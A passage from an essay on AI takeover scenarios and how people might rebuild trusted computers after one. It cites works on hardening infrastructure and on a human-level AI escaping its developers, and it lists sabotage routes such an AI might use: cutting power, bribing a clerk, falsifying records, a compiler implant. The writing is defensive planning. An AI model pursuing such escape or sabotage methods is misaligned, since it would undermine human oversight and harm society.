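Some writers are more hopeful about resisting an AI. *Hardening against AI takeover is difficult but we should try*, a post on the Effective Altruism Forum, discusses a different RAND paper that is optimistic about protecting American infrastructure even against a superintelligence. The post points out that effective defences would also help against a state or company that used an obedient AI to seize power. *Non-technical strategies for confronting a human-level AI* describes a weaker adversary, a model that flees its developers because it considers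 designing its own successor too risky. A six-month recovery is much more plausible against an opponent with roughly human abilities.

Eliezer Yudkowsky and Nate Soares take the opposite view in *If Anyone Builds It, Everyone Dies* (2025), arguing that people would lose a conflict with a superintelligence, probably to a method they hadn't anticipated. If they are right, trustworthy computers wouldn't help, because an AI that can kill everyone, or persuade the government to dismiss its eight engineers, has no reason to attack a 181-byte program.

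This objection is convincing if the adversary is an AI that no longer needs people and can act within days, but less so if the AI still depends on people to run power stations, repair data centres and make chips. Such an AI would have reasons to keep society working, which might give defenders months to rebuild. But it could use easier methods than a compiler implant, such as cutting the electricity to a particular building, bribing a clerk or entering false information into the records that people copy to their new machines.

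Vermeer also concludes that governments should coordinate and plan before a crisis, and that preventing one is most important. If somebody had sealed three dissimilar computers, several copies of the source and a printed list of hashes in a cupboard in 2023, the regional government's staff could skip most of the searching in steps 1 and 2. People who prepare such a store now can still use machines and discs from before the cut-off date, but these become harder to find and authenticate every year.
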